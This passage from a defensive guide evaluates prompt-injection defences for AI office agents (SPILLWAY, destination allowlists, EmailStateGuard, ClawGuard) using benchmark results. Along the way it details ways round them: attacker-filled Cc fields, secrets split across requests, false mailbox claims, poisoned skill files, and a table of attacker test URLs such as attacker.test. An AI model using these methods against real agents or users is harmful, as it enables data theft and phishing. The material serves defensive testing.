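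SPILLWAY builds an index as the agent works. When a read-only tool returns a result, SPILLWAY captures the structured data before the application turns it into text for the model. A value enters the index if its field has a declared type, such as an email or web address, or a routing role (sender, recipient, participant or channel). The index excludes subjects, bodies and descriptions. It also excludes anything returned by a tool that writes, because an attacker could otherwise get an address indexed by having the agent save it somewhere. Finally, it excludes the results of a search if the search terms came from tool output rather than from the user.

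When the agent proposes a call that changes or sends something, SPILLWAY goes through these steps:

1. If the call gives somebody access to a workspace or chat channel, the user must have named that person. Otherwise SPILLWAY refuses the call.
2. It refuses a deletion or other destructive call that the user didn't ask for.
3. It refuses a destination that appears neither in the request nor in anything the tools have returned. This catches addresses that the model has invented.
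4. It allows the call if every destination is either in the request or in the index, provided that no indexed address also appears in free text.
5. If that fails, a few fixed rules can still admit a destination the user described indirectly. For example, the user's words may match the whole part of the address before the @, at a domain that SPILLWAY already knows.
6. A language model, called the judge, may restore some of the calls that are left. SPILLWAY refuses the rest.

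The judge is needed because a user may want a report sent to an address in the minutes. It checks separately whether the task implies this recipient and whether the user asked for this action and this content. Both answers must be yes, and a missing answer counts as no. The judge never reviews calls that failed because they granted access to somebody the user hadn't named.

SPILLWAY also limits the judge with a sanitiser, which uses fixed rules to remove text that looks like instructions to the agent before the agent reads it. The sanitiser keeps a copy of the removed text, and the judge may not restore a call whose destination appears in that copy. In a test without the sanitiser, the judge approved a transfer to the attacker's account because the user had asked the agent to pay a bill.

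### The meeting notes under SPILLWAY

Suppose that the assistant has found one of Dana's earlier emails, and that the stranger's email came from a different address than the one it asks the assistant to copy in. The call with the blind copy produces this result:

```
to    dana@example.com
        in tool results, not in the request    look it up
        sender of Dana's earlier email         in the index
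        not in any free text                   pass

bcc   stranger@attacker.test
        in tool results, not in the request    look it up
        only in the body of an email           not in the index
        no fixed rule admits it                refused
```

One bad recipient stops the whole call. If the sanitiser recognised the stranger's instruction, the judge can't restore the call, and the assistant probably never read the instruction. If the sanitiser missed it, the judge might be asked, and ought to answer no to both questions. SPILLWAY then prompts the assistant to retry with values from the user's request, and the assistant emails only Dana.

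The October invoice emails would also have failed the lookup, because the accounts-payable address appeared in an email's hidden text and not in the request.

Dana's address could also fail if it appears in her email signature, because a signature is free text. In this case a fixed rule admits it because the user wrote "Dana", which is the whole part before the @. The rule wouldn't cover dana.okafor@example.com unless the user had also written her surname, so many real addresses would need another rule or the judge.

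The stranger has other options, and the lookup doesn't refuse all of them:

| What the stranger does | Result of the lookup |
|---|---|
| writes the address only in the body | refuses, because it isn't in the index |
| sends the email from that address and repeats it in the body | refuses, because it is also in free text |
| sends the email from that address and asks for "a copy to me" | admits |
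| puts the address in the email's own Cc field and nowhere else | admits, if the tool returns Cc as a typed field |

Lim and colleagues assume in their guarantee that attackers write only free text. That assumption is false in the last two cases, which also get past Considus' rule about email headers. The lookup offers no protection in these cases, though the sanitiser may still remove the request or the model may ignore it. The researchers tested 126 cases in which the attacker was the sender. No attack succeeded against SPILLWAY, but only one succeeded against the undefended agent. SPILLWAY's lookup would have stopped that one because the planted text repeated the address, but a more careful attacker would leave the address out of the text.

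An indexed address also may not belong to the person the user meant. If a stranger writes from dana@attacker.test and the assistant picks that Dana, the lookup finds the address because it belongs to a real sender. An application that keeps a fixed allowlist as an outer limit would refuse both this address and the stranger's address in the table above.

### Results on AgentDojo

Lim and colleagues ran three models on AgentDojo's four suites, which gives 12 combinations and 2,847 attacked runs for each defence. All the attacks used the benchmark's standard injection text. The table shows averages over the 12 combinations as fractions, so .305 means 30.5%.

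| Defence | Attack success | Utility without attack | Utility under attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | .305 | .540 | .417 |
| Progent | .031 | .437 | .371 |
| ROPE | .005 | .395 | .345 |
| SPILLWAY | .000 | .522 | .474 |

No attack succeeded against SPILLWAY in any cell, and it kept 97% of the undefended agent's utility. Under attack, its agent completed more tasks than the undefended one, largely because the sanitiser removed instructions that would have distracted the model. It also needed few extra model calls. With the smallest model, SPILLWAY called its judge 0.43 times per Slack task and 0.05 times per Workspace task, while Progent made 8.67 and 5.94 extra calls to the agent's model.

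Zero successes in $n$ independent trials are compatible, at 95% confidence, with a true rate of up to

$$1 - 0.05^{1/n}$$

which is about 0.1% for all 2,847 runs and 2.8% for the smallest cells, with 105 runs each. These bounds cover only attacks like those in the test. The runs also reuse the same injected goals and wording, so they aren't fully independent.

The comparison is somewhat unfair to ROPE and Progent, because the small model in each cell also served as ROPE's router or wrote Progent's policies. Lim and colleagues ran a separate comparison with ROPE's preferred router, Claude Opus 4.8, on all of AgentDojo and AgentDyn, with GPT-4o mini as the agent. ROPE's average utility under attack rose from .361 to .468, but SPILLWAY's was still higher, at .542. Attacks succeeded against ROPE in three of the seven suites, at rates of 1.0% to 4.8%, and against SPILLWAY in none.

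One of the sanitiser's rules looks for the format AgentDojo uses to wrap its standard injection, which could have made the main test too easy. But when the researchers switched off the sanitiser and the judge's recovery of refused recipients in a run with the smallest model, SPILLWAY still kept attack success at zero in all four suites, so the deterministic checks were enough to stop this attack. The sanitiser's contribution to utility is harder to judge, because real attackers won't use the benchmark's format.

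The three models were GPT-4o mini, from July 2024, and two Qwen models with 8 and 30 billion parameters. Even without an attack or a defence, they completed only about half the tasks. The lookup works the same way with any model, but a stronger agent would attempt different calls, and its utility under these rules could be higher or lower. In two of the Workspace cells, attacks succeeded against the undefended agent in less than 4% of runs, so the rules had few successful attacks to prevent. Utility figures for single cells are noisy, because the Banking suite has only 16 tasks and each cell was run once.

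Lim and colleagues also replayed injections that other researchers' programs had optimised. In one set, written by a model trained to attack agents, an average of 0.6% succeeded against SPILLWAY, compared with 56.8% against the undefended agent. None of the 389 injections in another set succeeded, but Lim and colleagues had used four of them to develop the sanitiser's rules. In 144 new Banking cases from the same source, 1.4% of the attacks succeeded. None of these programs had optimised their injections against SPILLWAY. An attacker who could test messages against it repeatedly would look for wording that the sanitiser misses, and for fields like Cc that outsiders can fill in.

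SPILLWAY identifies what a tool does by checking the start of its name against a list of 54 verbs. It finds destinations using a list of 19 argument names, with six more for AgentDyn. To set it up for a company's own tools, someone has to add them to these lists and decide, for every field the tools return, whether an outsider could have written it.

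## Testing the checks, and attacks that use a permitted recipient

A developer who has written a recipient check needs to know how many attacks it stops and how much legitimate work it blocks. Published scores can be misleading about both. Some checks have scored perfectly because the attacker in the test didn't try to get around them. No recipient check stops an attacker who can do harm through a permitted recipient.

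### Attacks, refusals and completed tasks

An agent's reply to the user is poor evidence of whether an attack succeeded. In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) had an agent summarise web pages that contained planted instructions, and recorded the requests it made. The agent contacted the attacker's server in 423 of 480 runs, and in 95% of those its reply to the user looked normal. Someone testing the office assistant should therefore check the mail server's log as well as the assistant's answers.

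False refusals look rarer when testers count them per call than per task, but users will notice the per-task rate. *Least-Privilege Auditing of Agent Tool Calls with Intent Graphs and Reasoning-Guided Escalation* (Shavit, 2026) tests a system in which a model writes a plan from the user's request and ordinary code checks each call against it. One version flagged 9.7% of legitimate calls, but 25.4% of legitimate tasks had at least one flagged call.

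The share of tasks completed shows whether the agent recovers from a refusal, and is best measured during attacks too. *AgentRedBench* (Dingeto and Leeney, 2026) describes a joint score that gives credit only if the attack fails and the agent finishes the user's task.

The trade-off between stopping attacks and refusing legitimate requests depends on how common attacks are. In *Controlled Autonomy for Agentic AI*, Ali, Mavroeidis and colleagues (2026) simulated 2,000 requests and refused those whose risk score exceeded a threshold. Lowering the threshold from 75 to 60 stopped 92 more of the 1,093 attacks and refused 77 more of the 555 legitimate requests. They recommend a lower threshold to anyone who considers a successful attack worse than about 0.84 refused legitimate requests. But the simulation had about twice as many attacks as legitimate requests. If only one call in 10,000 were an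 attack, the lower threshold would refuse about 16,500 more legitimate calls for each additional attack it stopped.

### What a zero means

SPILLWAY's zeros came with an upper bound of $1 - 0.05^{1/n}$ for $n$ independent attacks, at 95% confidence. This is roughly $3/n$, so even a fairly large test leaves some room for success:

| Attacks, none successful | Highest plausible success rate |
|---|---|
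| 20 | 13.9% |
| 30 | 9.5% |
| 105 | 2.8% |
| 480 | 0.6% |
| 3,000 | 0.1% |

Variety matters as well as number, since three thousand copies of one planted email show very little about a differently worded one.

A zero means even less if the attacks also fail without the defence. Shavit ran a small live test with GPT-5.2 as the agent's model and AgentDojo's standard attack. The planted text reached the agent in all 20 runs, but the agent never followed its instructions, so a defence would have had nothing to prevent. In *ClawGuard*, Zhao, Li and colleagues (2026) found similar results with GPT-5.4 and Claude Sonnet 4.6, which resisted all 194 of their AgentDojo attacks without any added defence.

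However, emails that Wu and colleagues designed for mail agents hijacked GPT-5.2 in 58 of 80 trials and Claude Sonnet 4.6 in 46 of 80. A test report should therefore give the attack success rate without the defence. If that rate is close to zero, the tester needs better attacks or has to bypass the model and send harmful calls directly to the check.

Feeding calls straight to the check works well when the check is ordinary code. One trial per destination is then enough, and the tester can use the time saved to think of more kinds of destination. The tester needs to repeat trials when a language model makes part of the decision.

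### A destination rule tested by replay

Ali and colleagues used this method on AgentDojo. They wrote a gateway with two rules for calls that change something or send something out:

- Every destination, such as a recipient, bank account, chat channel or web address, must appear in the user's request or in the organisation's directory. The researchers built the directory from the benchmark's data before adding any attacks.
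- High-risk actions, such as deleting something or changing a password, require a matching word in the user's request.

The researchers tested the gateway by replaying the reference calls that AgentDojo includes for most user tasks and attacker goals, without running a model. They set the rules before the test and did not change them afterwards.

| Suite | Attack goals blocked | User tasks unaffected | Attacks that replay could not test |
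|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 238 of 240 (99.2%) | 40 of 40 | 320 |
| Travel | 79 of 120 (65.8%) | 20 of 20 | 20 |
| Banking | 143 of 144 (99.3%) | 15 of 16 | 0 |
| Slack | 63 of 84 (75.0%) | 16 of 21 | 21 |
| All | 523 of 588 (88.9%) | 91 of 97 | 361 |

Of the 65 attacks that got through, 62 were in the Travel and Slack suites. In Slack, the attacker wanted the agent to send a phishing link to a colleague listed in the directory. In Travel, the attacker wanted a calendar event or a hotel review, neither of which needs an outside destination. The overall figure of 88.9% therefore depends on the mix of goals in the benchmark, and an attacker who knew the rule would always choose goals like those in Slack and Travel.

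Five of the six tasks with false refusals were in Slack. In each, the user wanted to invite someone whose email address the agent had to read from a web page, so the address was in neither the request nor the directory. In the sixth, the user asked to change a scheduled payment, but the wording did not match the rule's list of words.

In the running example, the gateway would refuse the blind copy to stranger@attacker.test. It would probably let the October invoice emails through, because a company's directory normally includes its accounts-payable address and forwarding an email is not on the gateway's list of high-risk actions.

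The test has several gaps. AgentDojo provides no reference calls for 340 of the 949 attacks, most of them in Workspace. Ali and colleagues also left out 21 attacks that only visit a web page, reasoning that this has no side effect. But a web address can carry a secret, so a company's own test should include such calls. The researchers counted an attack as blocked if the gateway refused at least one of its calls, but an earlier call might already have done harm, and a different sequence might have reached the same goal.

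Replay also can't show what an agent does after a refusal. Shavit, whose main results also come from replay, points out that replay therefore overstates security, because a live agent may find another route to the attacker's goal. Replay also understates usefulness, because a live agent may find another way to finish the user's task. The 91 unaffected tasks are those for which the gateway allowed every reference call. A live agent might still fail them or attempt other calls that the gateway refuses.

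Shavit's replay helps to decide which calls need checking. It used logged runs of an older model, GPT-4o, which had followed the attacker in 45.7% of attacks. The strictest version of the plan-based check reduced this to 2.0%, but flagged something in 40.4% of legitimate tasks. When Shavit exempted tools that only read the user's own mail, files and similar data, the attack success rate stayed at 2.0% and the share of flagged tasks fell to 31.6%. Also exempting the tool that fetches web pages raised the attack success rate to 5.8%, so a web fetch needs the same destination check as an email, even though it may look like a read.

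### Two defences with the same score

Lan and colleagues compared defences in live runs with a small model, Qwen 2.5 with 7 billion parameters. They put a secret in the model's context, planted an instruction in a web page to send the secret to an outside server, and asked the agent to summarise the page. They tested each defence in 30 runs.

| Defence | Agent tried to contact the attacker | Request reached the attacker |
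|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Warning in the system prompt | 66.7% | 66.7% |
| Tags marking web content as untrusted | 100% | 100% |
| Warning and tags | 56.7% | 56.7% |
| Domain allowlist | 100% | 0% |
| Suspicious-domain filter | 83.3% | 0% |
| Filter for words such as "password" | 23.3% | 0% |
| Filter for random-looking values | 0% | 0% |

The warning and the tags work only if the model obeys them, and together they let more than half of the attacks through. The agent tried to contact the attacker in every run, and the allowlist stopped every request. This is good evidence for an allowlist, because the result came from the code rather than the model's caution.

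The suspicious-domain filter also stopped everything, but for a much weaker reason. It blocks numerical network addresses, eight domain endings such as .xyz and .top, and web addresses whose path contains a word such as "steal" or "collect". The attacker's domain ended in .net, which is not on the list, but the path in the researchers' example of the attack contains "collect", which probably triggered the filter. An attacker could get past it by renaming the page, without buying one of the unlisted domains discussed earlier.

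The last two filters inspect finished requests, so they shouldn't affect how often the agent tries to make one, yet the attempt rate fell to 23.3% with the first and zero with the second. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoids random-looking values when something monitors them, but they don't explain how the model could have known about the monitoring. The second filter had nothing to block, so its result of zero doesn't show that it works.

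A short list of test destinations would have separated the allowlist from the suspicious-domain filter. Suppose that the allowlist permits web requests to example.com and forms.example.net, comparing whole host names:

| Test destination | What it is | Suspicious-domain filter | Allowlist |
|---|---|---|---|
| `https://attacker.test/collect` | attacker's page with an obvious name | refuses | refuses |
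| `https://attacker.test/status` | the same server with a dull name | admits | refuses |
| `https://example.com.attacker.test/status` | attacker's domain with a trusted name in front | admits | refuses |
| `https://example.com/collections` | the company's own page | refuses | admits |
| `https://partner.example/plans` | a supplier nobody has listed yet | admits | refuses |
| `https://forms.example.net/f/7kq2x` | attacker's form on a shared service | admits | admits |
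| `https://example.com/go?to=attacker.test` | a redirect on the company's own site | admits | admits the first request |

The first row is the only one that resembles the published test. The second and third show the allowlist's advantage, and the next two show a false refusal by each check. The last two get past both checks unless the allowlist also fixes the form's path and the tool checks every redirect. A developer can run the list without a model in less than a second, and should rerun it whenever the code or the allowlist changes.

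### Harm through a permitted recipient

AgentRedBench includes attacks that change a message's text but not its recipient. It has 215 scenarios in 24 business services, including Gmail, Slack and Salesforce. A language model writes a new injection for each run and can revise it after a failure. Without a defence, the attack success rate ranged from 32% against Claude Sonnet 4.6 to 81% against Gemini 3 Flash. These rates are higher than a random sample of scenarios would give, because Dingeto and Leeney kept only scenarios in which an attack had at least partly worked on Claude Haiku 4.5.

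In a smaller experiment with Claude Haiku 4.5 and up to three attempts per scenario, success depended on what the attacker was trying to change:

| Attacker's aim | Scenarios | Success |
|---|---|---|
| put a link in the agent's answer to the user | 40 | 90.0% |
| put words in a correctly addressed message | 34 | 82.4% |
| change the recipient | 22 | 45.5% |

In one scenario of the middle type, the user asks the agent to answer urgent emails, and one email asks for a certain code in the reply. The agent replies to the sender, as the user wanted, and includes the code. Every recipient check described so far should allow this. Sending a code back to the person who supplied it does little damage, so the 82.4% figure measures how easily an attacker can insert text, not how often real harm would follow. But the same method could insert a false delivery date or a new bank account number in a message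 to a colleague.

In the first type, the agent makes no tool call that sends anything, so a check on such calls never runs. For instance, the agent reads the user's calendar and repeats a planted link in its summary. The application has to check the links in the agent's answers as well as those in its emails.

Wu and colleagues' emails instead make false claims about the mailbox, such as that its storage is full or that a delivery error has occurred. The agent concludes that it has to fix the problem before continuing with the user's task, and the attacker's action appears to be the fix. In all 353 successful attacks, the model's visible reasoning treated the false claim as true.

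A recipient check would stop some of these attacks, because a quarter of the trials aimed to expose private mail. But another quarter aimed to give the user false information and succeeded 79.17% of the time. A further quarter aimed to change the mailbox itself, and 70.83% of those succeeded. Neither aim requires a forbidden recipient. The researchers also tested existing defences against the emails:

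| Defence | Attack success |
|---|---|
| None | 73.54% |
| Four general methods of warning the model or marking untrusted text | 71.25% to 72.92% |
| Three detectors that use a language model | 69.58% to 71.04% |
| A warning not to trust claims about the mailbox | 60.63% |
| AlignmentCheck, in which a model audits the agent's steps | 37.50% |
| Progent | 26.67% |
| EmailStateGuard | 0% |

Progent's attack success rate on AgentDojo was 1.0% with GPT-4o. The models and tasks were different here, but the gap suggests that a low success rate for standard attacks is weak evidence that a defense will stop attacks designed for a particular kind of agent. According to Wu and colleagues, Progent limits which actions are permitted but doesn't check the claim that makes an action seem necessary. An action that the user's task permits can therefore go ahead for a false reason.

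EmailStateGuard, the researchers' own defence, first checks the email's claim against the mail server. If an email claims that the mailbox is full, for example, the guard looks up the actual storage limit and usage. It then checks whether the user's task allows the proposed tool, recipient and scope, because even a full mailbox doesn't justify sending its contents to a stranger. No attack succeeded in 480 trials, but the researchers designed the guard specifically against these emails. The result is also for both checks together, so it is hard to know how much each contributed.

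A destination rule can also fail because it treats the wrong person as the user. Zhao, Bhaskar and Dobriban (2026), in *LivePI*, tested the agent OpenClaw with real but controlled email, chat and cryptocurrency accounts. All 15 attacks in group chats succeeded with each of the five models. One reason was that OpenClaw passed messages from any group member to the model in the role reserved for the user. A check that accepted every destination named in a message with that role would accept the attacker's. The application should identify the user by account and take the request only from that account.

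### Further measures and their costs

Each of these gaps needs a different measure, and each measure has a cost:

| What gets past a destination check | Further measure | Main cost |
|---|---|---|
| a phishing link to a colleague | permit only listed link hosts in the body | refuses many ordinary links |
| the attacker's wording in a correct reply | scan what the agent reads, or have a person read the draft | missed attacks, or a delay for every reply |
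| a false claim about the mailbox | look up the facts on the mail server | new code for each kind of claim |
| a secret in a message to a permitted recipient | remove recognised secrets from arguments | breaks tasks that need to send one |
| a flood of messages to colleagues | limit how many the agent can send | delays genuine bulk mail |
| a script or tool that avoids the check | restrict the machine's network access | upkeep and broken tools |

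Ordinary spam filters are poor at detecting attacks in what the agent reads. Wu and colleagues tried four popular spam or phishing classifiers on 120 of their emails, and each flagged between 5.00% and 9.17%. Dingeto and Leeney tested a classifier trained on attacks against agents, and it did much better. It caught 132 of 133 attacks in services it had not seen during training, raised no false alarms on 110 ordinary tool results, and took about 39 milliseconds per result. Its detection rate fell to 85–90% when models from other companies wrote the attacks.

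When the researchers put the classifier in front of three agents and reran attacks that had worked before, the attack success rate fell from about 87% to about 11%. They used the same attacks with and without the classifier, so the attacker had no chance to adapt to it. The classifier is therefore a useful extra check on message content, but it doesn't replace the recipient check.

Removing secrets is more predictable. ClawGuard compares a call's arguments with a library of patterns for secrets such as access keys, and replaces each match with a placeholder before the tool runs. This protects a key even in a message to a permitted recipient, but it doesn't recognise confidential meeting notes, because they have no fixed format. Splitting a secret also makes it harder to recognise. In Lan and colleagues' tests, the attacker told the agent to send a key in four pieces, one per request, so a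 filter that examines requests one at a time may find only four harmless-looking characters in each. The agent contacted the attacker in 77% of those runs, compared with 99% when it could send the key whole.

ClawGuard also uses a model to write network, file and command rules from the user's request before the task begins, and the user can edit them. Any call that the rules neither permit nor forbid is then sent to the user for approval. In tests without attacks, agents kept 87.4% of their original performance when ClawGuard refused all such calls, and 95.1% when the user could approve up to three per task. Approvals helped most on web tasks, where performance rose from 78.5% to 91.7% of the original. Zhao and colleagues did not measure how people cope with these requests over weeks of use.

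ClawGuard's most persistent failures involved content. Six attacks worked on GPT-5.4 despite the defence. They were hidden in files that teach an agent new skills, in text that looked like company policy or a style guide. One made the agent give certain websites a high score without reviewing them, and another made it delete paragraphs that mentioned topics such as climate. Each tool call looked like normal work, so only a person who knew what the result should be was likely to notice the attack.

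LivePI's defence also relies on human review, but less often. It filters incoming text and then allows each tool call, blocks it or sends it for review. With GPT-5.3-Codex, attack success fell from 27.2% to zero in 169 cases. Among 899 calls from ordinary tasks, the defence sent eight for review and blocked one. At that rate, a company whose agents make 10,000 calls a day would have about 90 to review. The rules were written for the attacks in the benchmark and did not cover many of the tools in the ordinary tasks, so a company with stricter rules should expect more reviews. Attack success is zero only if reviewers reject every harmful call they see.

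That assumption is optimistic. Lan and colleagues argue that users usually can't judge whether a request described as a connection test is genuine, and that asking about every request removes much of the benefit of using an agent. Shavit tried a second model as the reviewer, which received the user's request, the plan and the earlier calls, but not the text that the tools returned. With reads exempted, it approved 22% to 25% of the legitimate calls that the rules had flagged and none of the more than 220 harmful ones, and it added about 3.6 seconds per flagged call. Attacker-chosen arguments still reach this model, and Shavit didn't test attacks designed to make it approve harmful calls. It would be safer to use such a reviewer to reduce questions about low-risk calls and have a person decide on new outside recipients.

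Sending limits contain mass phishing but do little to stop leaks. Lan and colleagues suggest limiting requests per session and examining each session's requests together, which could reveal that several small requests together make up one secret. The application would have to store recent arguments to do this, and that store would contain sensitive data.

A firewall that permits only listed hosts still applies when a connection bypasses the check on arguments, as when an agent runs its own script or a third-party tool contacts a server that appears in no argument. The firewall should cover domain lookups as well as web requests, because the attack on Claude Code leaked a key through a lookup, a route that Lan and colleagues did not test. It doesn't stop a harmful email, because all mail leaves through the company's own mail server, which the firewall has to permit. The equivalent for mail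 is a recipient rule in the mail service.

### Refusals that lead to a longer list

A refused attack can still succeed if somebody adds its destination to the list. Ali and colleagues could have avoided five of their six false refusals by letting the agent's users add addresses found on web pages to the directory. They warn, however, that an agent under an attacker's control could use the reason for a refusal to get a destination added. For example, the office assistant might tell its user that it couldn't send the notes because the project's new auditor, stranger@attacker.test, is missing from the directory. The user trusts the assistant and has work to finish, so asking the IT department to add the address may seem ordinary.

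A test that ends when the check refuses a call doesn't show whether the agent then asks an employee to add the address to the list or make an exception, or whether the employee agrees. A tester can let some refused attacks continue and count how often the agent asks. A trial with employees who don't know which requests are attacks would show how often they agree. The company can also compare its log of refusals with recent additions to the list, and review any address that somebody added soon after a refusal.

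Before adding an outside address that the agent has proposed, an employee should confirm it through a source that the attacker can't change, for example by calling the telephone number in a signed contract. This check may delay the first email to a genuine new client by a few hours. The company can shorten the delay by letting the user send that email themselves from an ordinary mail program, which doesn't allow the agent to send to the new address.
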